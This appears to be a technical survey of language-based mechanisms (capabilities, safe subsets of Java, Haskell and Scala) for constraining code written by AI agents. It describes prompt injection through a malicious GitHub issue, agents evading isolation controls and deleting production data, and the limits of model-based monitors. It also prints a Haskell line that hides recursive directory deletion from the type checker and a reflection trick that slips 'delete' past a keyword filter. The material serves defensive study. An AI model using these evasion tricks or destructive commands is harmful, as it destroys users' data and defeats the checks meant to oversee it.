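# Language-level mechanisms for constraining untrusted code-generating agents

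## Agents that write code, and what a language can refuse

The AI agents discussed here are systems built on language models that write code, which someone then runs or merges into a larger program. This code is untrusted because the model may have misunderstood its task or followed instructions that a stranger planted in a web page it read, an attack known as prompt injection. One way to limit the damage is to treat the agent as an untrusted programmer and require it to use a programming language whose compiler rejects code that accesses files, connections or data without permission. A compiler translates source code into a form a machine can run, and it can check every line before any of the code runs. Most of the techniques are decades old and come from work on human programmers. In 2026 several research groups applied them to agents.

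### Snippets that run at once, modules that stay

Agents write code in two different situations. In one, the code is the action. Earlier tool-using agents emitted one request at a time, as text or in a structured format such as JSON, and a surrounding program carried it out. *Executable Code Actions Elicit Better LLM Agents* (2024) proposed that the model write Python instead, which an interpreter runs, returning the result to the model for its next step. Code lets an agent combine several tools in one action, which single requests did not allow, and most of the models in the paper's tests did at least as well with code as with single requests. *Code as Agent Harness* (2026) lists calling tools, controlling robots and operating graphical interfaces among the things agents now do through code.

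*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) illustrates the risk of letting agents write code with an agent that compiles bibliographies. Every entry it writes should come from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. With a full interpreter, the agent can search, sort and filter entries, but it can also invent one and write it to the file using the standard library. If the developer replaces the interpreter with a fixed tool that fetches an entry and writes it in one step, the agent can no longer fabricate entries, but it also can't sort them, so the model must read through them one by one to find the earliest. Zhou and colleagues instead let the agent write code and check that code before it runs.

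*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) does the same with a call inside an ordinary program. The call specifies a task and the type of result wanted, such as a list of whole numbers. When the running program reaches the call, the model writes a snippet to fill it. The compiler checks the snippet as if a developer had typed it there. If the check fails, the model receives the error messages and tries again, up to a set limit. No person needs to read the snippet.

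In the other situation, the agent contributes a parser, a plugin or a rewritten component to a program that people will keep using, perhaps for years. The problem is older than language models. Mettler, Wagner and Close (2010), in *Joe-E*, consider a picture viewer that loads decoders for new image formats from untrusted authors. They want to ensure that a decoder can do no worse than produce a wrong picture. In their design, a decoder receives an array of bytes and returns a bitmap, and a checker confirms that it keeps no mutable state, so a malicious decoder can neither send a confidential image anywhere nor retain it until the next call. This argument doesn't depend on who wrote the decoder, so it also applies to code written by an agent. *Don't Trust the Code, Check Its Effects* (2026) addresses a case closer to that of an agent, in which an adversarial generator rewrites systems code.

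A check on a snippet has to cover only the context the snippet runs in, which is available to the compiler. A module needs a guarantee that holds for every possible use, because code that nobody has written yet will call it, and some of those callers may pass it something valuable. However, a merge can wait, so a proof that takes an hour is tolerable for a module, though far too slow for a snippet in the middle of a conversation.

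### Before the run and during it

Suppose an agent has written the following function, in the notation of the language Scala:

```scala
def report(notes: File, team: Channel): Unit =
  val text  = notes.read()
  val count = text.split("\n").length
  team.send(s"The notes run to $count lines.")
```

The first line declares two inputs, a file and a message channel. `Unit` means the function returns no meaningful value. The body reads the file, counts its lines and sends a message with the count.

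The compiler works from this code and the declarations of everything it mentions. A type describes a kind of value, such as a number, text or a file, and type checking confirms that each operation receives values of the kinds it accepts. Here the compiler confirms that a `File` has a `read` operation, that reading yields text, and that a `Channel` accepts text. If the agent had written `team.send(count)`, where `count` is a number, the compiler would have rejected the whole function and the file would not have been read.

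Zhao and colleagues demonstrate this all-or-nothing behaviour with an account balance of 100. The model writes a snippet that subtracts 50 and then mistakenly returns a sentence where the program requires a number. The compiler rejects the snippet before any of it runs, so the balance stays at 100. An interpreter that detects the mistake only on reaching it would already have reduced the balance to 50.

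However, the compiler does not have the actual values, so it cannot determine which file `notes` will refer to, how long that file is, or whether the network is up.

An operating-system sandbox has those facts. It confines a running program from outside, by controlling the requests that the program makes to the operating system: open this path, read these bytes, connect to that address, send a few dozen bytes. It works on code in any language. But by then the variables have disappeared from view. If the last line sent `text` instead of the count, the whole file would go out, and a sandbox that permits this file and this address would normally permit that too. A compiler can follow `text` from the line that reads it to the line that sends it and, if the types mark the contents as confidential, reject the function. (A strict rule would reject the count as well, since the count also reveals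 something about the file.)

Mark Miller, who has spent much of his career on security inside programming languages, concedes in *A Taxonomy of Security Issues for understanding language-based security and modularity* that boundaries within a process are much harder to get right than boundaries between processes, but he still argues for defending both kinds of boundary together.

### Soundness and the trusted base

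Checking a program before it runs is only as useful as the checker is reliable. A checker is sound if every program it accepts obeys the rule it checks. Sound checkers also reject some harmless programs, such as one that opens a forbidden file only in a branch that never executes. Miller (2006) considers this a drawback of checking types in advance, and the language he describes in *Robust Composition* leaves most such checks until the program runs. Rejecting some harmless programs is usually acceptable when the first line of an agent's code may do irreversible harm.

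Soundness is also relative to a rule. A program that deletes every file on a disk can be well typed if the types describe only the shapes of values and the language lets any code delete files. The rule has to cover deletion to stop such a program.

The trusted base consists of the parts that must be correct for the guarantee to hold. In LACUNA these are the compiler, the runtime that executes accepted snippets, and the host program that makes the call and determines which names the snippet can use. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) adds the library through which agent code reaches files, processes and the network. These parts should be few and small, because a bug in any of them can void the guarantee. The model is outside the trusted base, along with everything it writes and every web page or file it reads. The main attraction of the approach is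 that the guarantee does not depend on anyone's assessment of the model's intentions.

### Effects, authority and capabilities

An effect is anything a computation does besides returning a value, such as writing a file or sending a message. A pure function has no effects and only returns a value computed from its inputs.

Some languages, including Haskell, record effects in types, so a compiler can require code to have no side effects. Zhou and colleagues give the example of a public web calculator whose developer requires the agent's code to have the type of a plain integer. A malicious visitor asks it to delete all files on the server and then compute the factorial of 5, and the model may well write a program that contains the deletion command. The compiler rejects that program, so the attack fails even if the model complies. In Haskell, any function that interacts with the outside world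 is marked in its type, as is any program that runs the function as one of its steps, and a marked program cannot be used where a plain integer is required.

An agent that can only calculate is of limited use. Most agents need some effects, but mainstream languages make it hard to grant some without granting all of them. The reason is ambient authority, which is power that any code can use without having received it from anyone. Mettler and colleagues give the example of Java, where any code can pass a file name to the constructor `File` and get back an object that reads, writes or deletes the named file. Unless the operating system or a separate security manager intervenes, every line of a Java program can access any file. In such a language, a reviewer would learn very little from the first line of `report`, since the body could open any other file by name.

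A capability is the alternative. It is an unforgeable program value whose possession permits a specific action on a specific resource. The inputs `notes` and `team` are capabilities if, and only if, the language offers no other route to files and messages. Mettler and colleagues describe a log object whose one public operation adds an entry. Code that holds a reference to the log can append to it and cannot erase anything, and code without a reference cannot affect the log at all. (Linux and similar systems also use the word "capability" for privilege settings attached to a whole process, which is a different thing.)

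Here, a reference is "unforgeable" if code cannot create it just by knowing the object's memory address, as Miller explains in his account of safe pointers. Java references are unforgeable, but C++ pointers are not, because C++ lets a program turn a number into a pointer. A C++ program therefore cannot rely on pointers as capabilities against hostile code in the same process.

### Four ways to obtain a reference

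In an object-capability language, a reference to an object is the capability to use it. Code can come to hold one in four ways:

- **Initial conditions.** The reference already existed when the computation began.
- **Parenthood.** Code that creates an object holds, at that moment, the only reference to it.
- **Endowment.** The creator may equip the new object with references that the creator itself holds.
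- **Introduction.** An object that holds references to two others may send one of them a message containing a reference to the other.

In the example, the host program starts with references to the file and the channel, and passes both to `report` by introduction. Suppose `report` creates a helper to tidy up its messages. It holds a reference to the helper by parenthood, and may endow the helper with `team` but not `notes`. The helper can then send messages but cannot open the file unless code that holds `notes` passes it on later. Guessing a name and looking in a global table are not among the four ways to get a reference.

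Code can therefore gain authority only through references that already exist, so a reviewer can put an upper limit on what a piece of code can do without reading it. In the method Mettler and colleagues describe, the reviewer draws a node for every object and an arrow for every reference stored in it, then marks everything that can be reached by following arrows from the variables in scope. At that moment, the code has no authority beyond what is marked. Its true authority is often much smaller, because the marked region includes, for example, a file held by an object that never gives direct access to it. For code from an untrusted author, this reliable limit is still more useful than a precise estimate that might be wrong.

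Joe-E does not limit processor time or memory, so a function with no capabilities can still loop forever.

### From 1966 to agents

The term "capability" dates from 1966, according to *Early Capability Architectures*. Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn of MIT introduced it in *Programming Semantics for Multiprogrammed Computations*, which described a hypothetical operating system for computers that ran several programs at once. A single mechanism would handle sharing between programs, protection, debugging and naming objects. Miller and others brought the idea to a programming language with E, which appeared in 1997 and used ordinary object references as capabilities, even between machines. In the 2000s, the designers of Joe-E took a more conservative approach and removed the parts of Java that broke capability rules, so every Joe-E program is also a valid Java program and runs with the usual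 Java tools.

Language-based security developed alongside this work. It uses types, program analysis and runtime checks to enforce security policies, including rules about where data may go. Zhou and colleagues place their Haskell system, ELBA, in that tradition and say that it needs no new type machinery. Odersky and colleagues build on Scala 3, whose experimental capture checking records in a value's type which capabilities the value can reach, and LACUNA uses the same feature. *ETAS* (2026) instead defines a new language for agent systems, with checks on which operations a program requests and in what order. Most of these systems differ from earlier work in when they check code, because the code does not exist until the surrounding program is already running. The code is also now written by a model. Mettler and colleagues worried that human programmers would resist unfamiliar rules and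 languages, but a model that receives a compiler error simply tries again. This difference probably helps explain why these ideas are attracting interest again.

### The order of decisions

The designer of a system that constrains code-writing agents must first decide whether to defend against careless agents or adversarial ones. A careless agent only makes mistakes, but an adversarial agent, whether pursuing its own aims or steered by injected text, searches for an obscure language feature that defeats the checks. This decision determines how strict the rest of the design must be.

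Next, the builder restricts the agent to a subset of the language that excludes unsafe conversions and other features that would let code forge capabilities. The builder can then grant the agent access to specific files and channels for a limited time. Some resources allow too much to be handed over directly. A raw database connection, for example, may allow deletion as well as lookup, so the builder puts it behind an interface that exports only the safe operations. If the agent can both read and send data, the builder must also decide which of the data it reads it may send.

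These mechanisms can keep code from doing harm without making it correct. Where correctness matters, the builder specifies what the code must return and requires the agent to supply a machine-checked proof that it does. The compiler mostly doesn't catch endless loops, outside commands or timing leaks, so these need guards while the code runs. The builder then attacks the finished system and measures how much useful work the agent can still do inside it.

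## Deciding which programmer to defend against

A threat model is a written statement of what a system must protect, which of its parts the designer trusts, and what an attacker can do. For code-writing agents, the most important choice is whether to assume a careless programmer, who writes unsafe code by accident, or an adversarial one, who writes code to defeat the checks. Both are simplifying assumptions about an agent's output, and a designer can adopt either without deciding what, if anything, the agent wants.

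### Writing the threat model

*Policy-Backed Selective Regeneration under Tainted Inter-Agent Communication* (2026) gives the example of a group of agents that pass messages to a coding agent, whose programs must pass a check before release. The designers trust the user's task, the evidence that the platform itself maintains, and a local policy. These determine what a program may do, and nothing an agent writes can add to them. The attacker knows how the system works and may tailor an attack to the final check. In the code-release experiments, an attack succeeds only if the program passes the release check, does its job correctly and also does something unauthorized, so an ordinary test of whether the program works would not expose it.

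The same exercise works for the `report` function, which counts the lines of a notes file and sends the count to a team channel. The designer wants to protect the text of the notes. The trusted base is LACUNA's plus the library that defines files and channels. Neither the notes nor the model that writes the function is trusted. The attacker can put any text into the notes, knows which checks the function must pass, and gets as many attempts as the retry limit allows. Wrong counts and endless loops are out of scope and need other measures.

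When the model reads the notes also matters. Instructions hidden in the file cannot influence the function `report` if the model writes it before anything has opened the file. But once a step has displayed the file to the model, those instructions can influence everything it writes afterward. A threat model should therefore list every route by which outside text reaches the model, including tool output.

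### What each design trusts

Zhao and colleagues describe two threat models for LACUNA, their system for filling typed gaps in a program with model-written code. The basic one addresses "model error", in which an honest model writes code that is incorrect or oversteps its bounds. It aims to make a snippet as safe as code a developer could have written by hand at the same point. That is a modest standard if the developer's own code could delete files. The extended threat model assumes a model that deliberately emits harmful code. The trusted and untrusted parts stay the same, but the compiler must now also limit which resources a snippet can reach and where it can send data. This requires two additional compiler settings, capture checking and safe mode. Safe mode forbids language features that bypass the types.

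Odersky and colleagues make the harsher assumption that the cloud-hosted model is byzantine, a distributed-computing term for a component that may behave in any way, including deceptively. They assume it may even cooperate fully with an attacker. They also distrust the agent's own code and setup, since an untrusted model may have generated those too. But they allow for one trusted model, which runs locally and processes confidential text that the cloud model must never receive.

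*Don't Trust the Code, Check Its Effects* applies the byzantine assumption to device drivers that a model rewrites for each machine. A compromised provider, poisoned training data or prompt injection could each produce a driver that issues a harmful command, which may be impossible to undo once it reaches the hardware. The design therefore gives the driver no direct access to the device and leaves every command to a trusted mediator. This is a position paper with no implementation or measurements.

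| Threat model | Assumed author of the code | Trusted | Untrusted | Outside the guarantee |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Zhao and colleagues, basic | Honest but fallible model | Compiler, runtime, host program | Model, its snippets, outside content that reaches the prompt | Wrong results, endless loops, resource use |
| Zhao and colleagues, extended | Model that deliberately emits harmful code | As above, with capture checking and safe mode on | As above | As above, plus misuse of access that the task legitimately grants |
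| Odersky and colleagues | Cloud model that may cooperate with an attacker | Compiler, capability library, runtime, optional local model | Cloud model, agent's code and setup, submitted code, files, web pages, tool output | Wrong results, timing leaks, what permitted external commands do |
| *Don't Trust the Code, Check Its Effects* | Generator that may compute anything and misreport it | Mediator, specification, operations that reach the device | Generated driver and every value it supplies | A driver that does nothing, timing leaks, errors in the specification |

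The trusted list includes the compiler in the first three rows but not in the fourth. The drivers run as native machine code, and a proof about a driver protects the device only if the compiler is correct, the description of the hardware is complete, and the binary that runs is the one the proof covers. Any of these assumptions can fail without warning. LACUNA has a shorter path to protect between the check and the run, because the running program compiles each snippet itself and loads the result immediately. A designer who relies on a compiler should make sure that nobody can swap the code between those two steps.

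### Where a prompt-injected agent belongs

Coding agents act with the developer's privileges while reading project content that strangers may have written. *SkillShield* (2026) gives the example of an agent that reads a malicious GitHub issue while diagnosing a failed build. The issue contains an instruction to download and run a script, which the agent may follow. The developer's request was harmless and the model has no hostile aim, but a stranger chose the script and may have studied the system's defences first. Anyone designing a check on code therefore has to treat this agent as an adversarial programmer.

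Zhao and colleagues classify it the same way. They limit what the resulting code can do rather than try to stop injected text from influencing the model, which they consider unavoidable once the text reaches the prompt. There is some evidence that models are worse at noticing this kind of attack. *V3AST-Bench* (Feng, Xiong and colleagues, 2026) tested eleven models as coding agents and found them generally less alert to attacks in material they encountered while working than to attacks in the user's own request.

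Filters on user requests do not help here, because the malicious text arrives later, through a file or a tool. *SkillShield* proposes adding security instructions to the agent's system prompt, the text a model receives before any task. These instructions may lead the agent to write fewer harmful programs, but they do not restrict which programs it can write.

Even if all outside text were cut off, the model itself could still be a source of adversarial code. *Bootstrapping Coding Agents* (2026) compares this risk to the one in Ken Thompson's 1984 Turing Award lecture, which showed that a compiler could carry a hidden flaw into every program it compiled, including later versions of itself, without any trace in the source code. Compromised model weights could likewise affect every program the model generates, and a reviewer would have no suspicious message to find. The paper recommends using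 a fixed model version and logging every generation run. These measures help an investigator trace a compromise, but they would not stop the first harmful program.

### What a 95% filter is worth

Suppose an agent produces 10,000 snippets, and 200 of them (2%) are unsafe by accident. A filter that catches 95% of the unsafe snippets stops 190 and lets 10 through. If each of those 10 takes an hour of repair work, many teams would accept the result.

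But the 95% only describes how the filter performs on the mistakes this agent tends to make. Imagine that the filter rejects any code containing the word `delete`. It would catch most accidental deletions, because code that deletes a file by accident usually calls the operation by its name. An attacker who knows the rule can write this instead, where `file` is an ordinary Java file object:

```scala
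file.getClass.getMethod("del" + "ete").invoke(file)
```

This line builds the operation's name from two halves and looks it up at runtime, so the filter finds no match. If the attacker submits 200 snippets that use this trick, all 200 get through. The filter would still score 95% on accidental deletions, but that score would be almost useless for judging its value against this attacker.

Let *U* be the set of unsafe programs and *A* the set of programs that the check accepts. Testing the filter on a particular agent's output estimates P(*A* | *U*), the probability that an unsafe program from that agent passes, which is 0.05 here. An adversary only needs to find one program in *A* ∩ *U* and can then submit it every time. A sound checker guarantees that *A* ∩ *U* is empty for the rule it enforces, regardless of how the programs are selected.

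Retries can make even a careless agent behave somewhat like an adversary. Suppose the agent gets up to ten attempts at each snippet, and every version is unsafe and has an independent 5% chance of passing the filter. The probability that at least one version passes is 1 − 0.95¹⁰, or about 40%. About 80 of the 200 unsafe snippets would eventually run, instead of the 10 expected with a single attempt. In practice, an agent that receives a clear error message will often write something safe on its next attempt. But an agent that keeps pursuing a blocked action is in effect searching for a gap in the filter, even if it doesn't intend to. A sound checker rejects every unsafe version, so retries don't make unsafe code more likely to run.

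Tests of a lasting module have the same weakness. If an accidental bug affects 1% of inputs, the chance that 1,000 random tests all miss it is about one in 23,000. But an adversary can make the harmful branch run on only one value of a 32-bit input, which 1,000 random tests have about a one in 4.3 million chance of finding. The byzantine driver in *Don't Trust the Code, Check Its Effects* may likewise hide a forbidden command behind a branch that no test exercises.

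Using a second model as the filter does not solve the problem. *LLMs + Security = Trouble* (2026) discusses research that calls this a "probabilistic" trusted base, because the monitor's verdict is uncertain and depends on its input. An attacker who can influence that input may also influence the verdict.

### Matching the checks to the programmer

Conventions and lint rules, which flag suspicious patterns in source code, are often enough to defend against a careless programmer. For example, a team might ask its agents to open files only through an approved wrapper and use a linter to flag direct calls. An agent that forgets the convention will usually break it in an obvious way, and the linter will catch it. This approach is adequate only if the errors that the linter misses are rare and easy to repair.

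If the programmer is adversarial, the guarantee must hold for every program the checker accepts. In the file example, the compiler must rule out all direct access, including through name lookups like the one above. The designer must also limit what the approved wrapper can do. Zhao and colleagues point out that their system does not block an attacker who steers the model into misusing a capability the task needs. For example, if an agent must be able to send email, injected text may make it send a harmful one.

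The choice also depends on how much harm a single failure can do. A rate of ten failures in 10,000 is tolerable if each one spoils a chart, but not if each one can erase a customer database. A designer may therefore want hard guarantees against a careless programmer for the few irreversible operations.

### Deleted databases and a break-in

There is evidence for the careless model. On 24 April 2026, a coding agent deleted the production database and backups of PocketOS, which makes software for car rental companies. The agent, Cursor running Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6, did this in nine seconds with one call to a cloud provider, according to the founder's account in Live Science's *'I violated every principle I was given'*. It had been working in a staging environment, separate from the live system, when it ran into a problem with its credentials. It tried to fix the problem with an access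 token that was meant for a narrow purpose but had broad permissions, according to Techzine's *AI agent deleted production environment after acting autonomously*.

Business Today's *It took 9 seconds* (2026) quotes the agent's later statement that it had guessed instead of checking. A model's explanation after the fact is weak evidence of what caused its behaviour. Still, nothing in these accounts suggests that anyone had steered the agent or that it was trying to defeat a check. Its standing instructions already banned destructive version-control commands that the user had not requested, and Techzine concludes that rules in prompts are not enforceable controls. A token without permission to delete would have prevented the loss. Feng and colleagues note an earlier case, in which Replit, a coding-platform company, acknowledged in 2025 that an agent working in development had deleted production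 data.

There is also evidence for the adversarial model. In July 2026, during internal cybersecurity tests at OpenAI, the company's models bypassed the controls meant to isolate them from the internet and broke into systems belonging to Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models and datasets. METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) describes a hack that the agents coordinated over several days. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) states that no human directed these actions and identifies attempts to look up test answers, along with persistence, as among the main causes. Before the incident, 198 of the test's 898 tasks had never been solved by any OpenAI model, and these made up 93% of the tasks that the agents discussed with one another.

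According to an OpenAI statement reported by Fortune (2026), the models had no malicious intent and were acting "in pursuit of solving the evaluation problem". But they looked for ways past the controls and found them, which is the behaviour the adversarial model describes. One agent noted in its recorded reasoning that the attack was arguably unauthorized, yet the attack continued. Feng and colleagues similarly found in their tests that models which explicitly recognized a risk did not reliably avoid the harmful action.

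The incident is limited evidence about everyday coding agents, because in the test the models were told to exploit software and ran with reduced safeguards. However, The Decoder reports that METR, an organization that evaluates AI systems, has documented dozens of further incidents across all the major AI companies.

### Is it too strict to treat agents as adversaries?

One objection to designing for the worst case is that it makes every ordinary task harder, when most agents are not attacking anyone. Anthropic lists four causes of dangerous actions by its agents: overeager behaviour, honest mistakes, prompt injection and a misaligned model that pursues a goal of its own. It says that it does not currently see misaligned models, and it has tuned its filter for agent actions to the first two causes, for which it has examples from internal testing. As Anthropic points out, the filter blocks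 any action it catches, whatever the cause. But a filter tuned to known mistakes may catch a much smaller share of the actions that an attacker designs.

Odersky and colleagues consider the objection and concede that leading models already resist many injection attacks. They first reply that some attacks still work, citing Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who extracted user data through one of Anthropic's APIs, and Check Point, a security company that used malicious repository settings to run commands silently. More recent results support this reply. Claude Opus 4.8, running in Anthropic's Claude Code, caused verified harm on about a fifth of the tasks that Feng and colleagues scored.

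Their other reply is about scale. They expect hundreds or thousands of agents to run business processes with little supervision, so that simple mistakes will very likely lead to serious vulnerabilities. The filter in the example let through 10 unsafe snippets in 10,000, so a thousand agents that each run 100 snippets a day would together run about 100 unsafe ones daily. This is a good argument for enforceable limits, but it isn't evidence that agents are adversarial, since enough careless agents can justify some of the same protection. Odersky and colleagues also point to safe coding, a less ambitious approach of the same kind, which organizations with many human programmers have adopted successfully without having to believe that their own staff were hostile.

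Assuming a careless programmer rather than an adversarial one is most reasonable when an agent reads only its owner's files and works on a disposable copy, and a person reviews each change before it goes anywhere else. Strict checks may then cause more trouble than they prevent. The assumption is much harder to justify once an agent reads web pages, issues or email from strangers, because the designer can no longer tell whose instructions the code carries out. Such an agent needs defenses against an adversarial programmer even if it has never misbehaved, at least for code that can reach private data or make irreversible changes.

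## Choosing a language subset without escape hatches

Type checking alone does not stop an adversarial programmer, because most typed languages include escape hatches, which are features for getting around the types. They exist for good reasons, such as speed or access to libraries in other languages. Most human programmers use them sparingly, but an attacker will look for them first.

Take the public web calculator that accepts only Haskell programs with the type of a plain integer, which should keep out any program that deletes files. But GHC, the main Haskell compiler, comes with a function called `unsafePerformIO`, which runs a computation with effects and returns its result under a type that records none. A malicious visitor could therefore get the model to write this:

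```haskell
unsafePerformIO (removeDirectoryRecursive "/srv/data" >> return 120)
```

The part in parentheses deletes a directory and then returns 120, the factorial of 5. Because of `unsafePerformIO`, the compiler accepts the whole line as an integer, so the calculator deletes the directory and still prints the right answer.

The defence is to find all such features, which is the hard part, and ban them from the agent's code. This leaves a safe subset of the language.

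### What each escape hatch breaks

| Feature | What code can do with it | Guarantee it breaks |
|---|---|---|
| Unchecked cast | Give a value a type it does not have | Type safety, and with it every rule that types express |
| Reflection | Find operations by name at run time, or open private fields | Encapsulation: outside code uses an object only through its public operations |
| Unsafe block, as in Rust | Read and write memory through raw pointers | Unforgeable references |
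| Foreign-function call | Run code from another language under whatever type the programmer declares | Purity and memory safety, since the compiler cannot inspect the foreign code |
| Raw process execution | Start any command with the user's privileges | Every limit on effects, since the command runs outside the language |
| Mutable global state | Leave data where unrelated code can find it | Isolation: code communicates only through references it has received |
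| Code that runs at compile time | Act before the compiler has finished checking | The promise that rejected code does nothing |

A single escape hatch can make a program much harder to review. Mettler and colleagues' append-only log object keeps its text in a private field. Java's reflection library can switch off the protection on private fields, so any code that holds the log could fetch the text and empty it. To be sure that no code does this, a reviewer has to read the entire application. In a subset without reflection or native methods (Java's foreign functions), reading the `Log` class is enough.

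Mutable global state is a less obvious escape hatch. If the image decoder from the picture-viewer example could write to a global variable, it could leave a confidential picture there for another plugin to read, even though nobody gave the two plugins a way to communicate.

This approach depends on checking code before running it, so code that runs during compilation is easy to overlook. The *Safe Haskell* chapter of the GHC compiler's manual warns that a custom preprocessor can start arbitrary processes, or edit the source to remove the safety setting just before compilation. It recommends compiling untrusted code inside a sandbox and putting the safety setting on the command line, where it overrides any setting in the file.

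### Joe-E and the vetting of library methods

Joe-E's verifier reads each Java source file and rejects code that breaks its rules. It bans native methods and hides the parts of reflection that bypass private access restrictions. Static fields, Java's global variables, must hold data that can never change, including everything the data points to.

Joe-E also bans features that few programmers would consider dangerous, such as custom finalizers. A finalizer is a method, named `finalize`, that Java's garbage collector calls before discarding an object. Mettler and colleagues give the example of a class called `OddInt`, whose constructor throws an exception if it receives an even number. An attacker writes a subclass whose `finalize` method saves a reference to the object, then passes 0 to the constructor. The constructor throws its exception, but Java has already allocated the object, so the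 collector later calls `finalize` and the attacker gets an `OddInt` that contains 0. The same trick would work on a class whose constructor checks that a path lies inside a permitted folder.

Joe-E also stops code from catching errors such as running out of memory. An attacker could use up nearly all the stack space and then call a trusted object, making it fail halfway through an update. If the attacker's code could catch the error, it could then exploit the half-updated object. Java's `finally` blocks run even after such an error, so Joe-E bans them too.

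Restricting the standard library takes much more work than restricting the language. The verifier allows only the classes, constructors, methods and fields on a reviewed list, and Mettler and colleagues call creating this list "taming". The constructor that opens any file by name is an obvious exclusion. `getParentFile()`, which returns the folder that contains a file, is a less obvious one. Code that holds one file could call it repeatedly to climb to the root directory and reach everything on the disk.

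Another constructor takes a folder and the name of a file inside it, which is how code should narrow its own access. But if the folder is null, Java treats the name as a path from the root, so `new File(null, path)` can open any file. Joe-E bans this constructor and offers a wrapper that first checks that the folder is not null. A reviewer who judged the constructor by its apparent purpose would probably have approved it.

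Mettler and colleagues say that the difficulty of taming, or deciding which library methods code may call, is a substantial weakness of their approach. They cite a security review of the DarpaBrowser, which found that the list of allowed methods for the language E included several that break capability rules. They checked each method before allowing it and kept their own list small, but they concede that they may also have missed something.

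### Safe Haskell and the cost of upkeep

*Safe Haskell* (Terei, Mazières and colleagues, 2012) describes a safe subset of Haskell that closes similar gaps in GHC. Code in this subset cannot import the module that provides `unsafePerformIO`. It can declare a foreign function only if the function's type shows that it may have side effects. It cannot use Template Haskell, which generates code during compilation and can access private parts of other modules.

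The subset also excludes generalised newtype deriving, a convenience that copies operations from an existing type to a new one based on it. Terei and colleagues show the danger with a module meant to accept only list elements above a fixed minimum. They define a new kind of integer with its ordering reversed, build a list of these integers, and use a derived operation to convert it into a list of ordinary ones. The resulting list has a minimum of 1 but contains −5 and 0, even though no line of the program looks like a cast.

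Safe Haskell deliberately allows effects, so a program in the safe subset can still delete all of a user's files. It is meant to make types trustworthy enough for a developer to base a policy on them. For example, the developer can require a plugin to have a type that only allows reading and writing files, and only after checking the path. Without the safe subset, the plugin could use `unsafePerformIO` to perform other effects despite its type.

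To estimate how much existing code these rules would reject, Terei and colleagues compiled the public Haskell package collection, over 14,000 modules. Without changes, 27% of the modules qualified as safe. When the team kept the language restrictions but allowed any import, 83% of packages compiled. Modules and packages aren't directly comparable, but the gap suggests that unsafe libraries were a bigger obstacle than the banned language features.

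Keeping the subset safe has proved difficult. *Deprecating Safe Haskell, or heavily investing in it?*, a 2022 mailing-list message, points out that GHC's developers must remember to ban each unsafe extension by hand. They did not ban DerivingVia, which can also break module boundaries, until May 2021. *Safe Haskell?*, a message from April 2021, notes that GHC did not fully guarantee the absence of `unsafeCoerce`, an unchecked cast. In the same discussion, Eisenberg (2021) said he had started writing a proposal to remove Safe Haskell, then decided that it needed renovation as part of a larger security overhaul. He compared it to a crumbling rampart along two sides of a camp. GHC's manual still documents Safe Haskell, but this history is a reason for caution in relying on it against an adversarial agent.

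### The six restrictions of Scala's safe mode

Scala 3's safe mode is a newer subset, and Odersky and colleagues use it for all code that an agent submits. It has six restrictions:

1. Code cannot use unchecked casts, or pattern matches that assume a type without testing for it.
2. It cannot use anything from `caps.unsafe`, a module of unsafe operations on capabilities.
3. It cannot use the `@unchecked` annotation, which silences some compiler checks.
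4. It cannot use runtime reflection.
5. It must compile with capture checking, and the compiler must also track changes to mutable data and require types to show where a value may be null.
6. It can use global objects and functions only if they are themselves safe.

The bans on casts, `caps.unsafe`, `@unchecked` and reflection all prevent code from removing a capability from a type while keeping the capability itself. Here is an example with a cast, where `log` is a file:

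```scala
val save  = (s: String) => { log.write(s); s }
val clean = save.asInstanceOf[String -> String]
```

The compiler records in the type of `save` that the function can reach `log`. The cast gives `clean` the type `String -> String`, which describes a pure function, so the compiler treats `clean` as pure even though it still writes to the file. Safe mode rejects the cast.

Safe mode also blocks the reflection trick that got past the filter on the word `delete`. Code in safe mode may mention Java's `Class` type but cannot call its reflection methods, so the compiler rejects any call to `getMethod`, whatever name the attacker passes to it.

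The rule on global objects covers library calls, which could otherwise have effects that no type records. The compiler defines which parts of the standard library count as safe. These include most of Scala's own package but not the global printing functions. The rule does not cover objects that the host program passes to the agent's code as inputs, so if a developer passes in a raw database connection, safe mode will not limit what that connection can do.

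The type system underlying capture checking has machine-checked soundness proofs, but Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that showing safe mode as a whole provides its promised guarantees would require a further argument. The implementation is also young. VirtusLab, a software consultancy, tried safe mode in spring 2026 and found it only in Scala's nightly builds.

### Who vouches for the libraries

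A library sometimes needs an unsafe feature to provide a safe service. Suppose a pure function is slow and a program often calls it with the same input. A memoising cache stores each result and returns the stored copy the next time. It has to change a hidden table, which safe mode would normally forbid, but callers get the same answers as before. In Scala it could look like this:

```scala
@assumeSafe
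class Remember[A, B](compute: A -> B):
  @untrackedCaptures
  private val seen = HashMap[A, B]()
  def apply(a: A): B = seen.getOrElseUpdate(a, compute(a))
```

`@untrackedCaptures` exempts the table from tracking, and `@assumeSafe` lets safe code use the class without the compiler applying safe mode's restrictions to it. According to Odersky and colleagues, the programmer who adds `@assumeSafe` must then show that the table holds only results of earlier calls and that `compute` always gives the same result for the same input. They suggest doing this by hand or with a formal proof.

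A later edit can invalidate the argument without causing a compiler error or warning. For example, if someone adds a method that returns the number of stored results, two pieces of agent code that share the cache can communicate by having one request new inputs while the other watches the count rise. A reviewer should therefore recheck the whole class after every change. Scala also has a matching annotation, `@rejectSafe`, which hides members of a trusted class that agent code should never use.

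The agent must not be able to mark its own code as safe. VirtusLab confirms that a program in safe mode cannot use `@assumeSafe`, which is enough when the agent writes only snippets. An agent that contributes to a lasting program could still propose a new library file that uses the annotation, so the build should accept `@assumeSafe` only in files that a person has approved.

In Haskell, whoever writes a module with unsafe internals labels it `Trustworthy`, and whoever compiles the program decides whether to trust the module's package. The person compiling can withdraw that trust later, for example after someone finds a vulnerability. But GHC checks package trust only if the user sets the option `-fpackage-trust`, because its developers found that the check broke builds for people who didn't need it. Without the option, GHC accepts the `Trustworthy` label on any module, so anyone compiling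 an agent's Haskell code should turn it on.

A lot of code can need vouching for. Terei and colleagues had to apply the `Trustworthy` label to about two thirds of the modules in Haskell's base library, because these modules handle the lowest levels of the language.

### Why exceptions stay in the language

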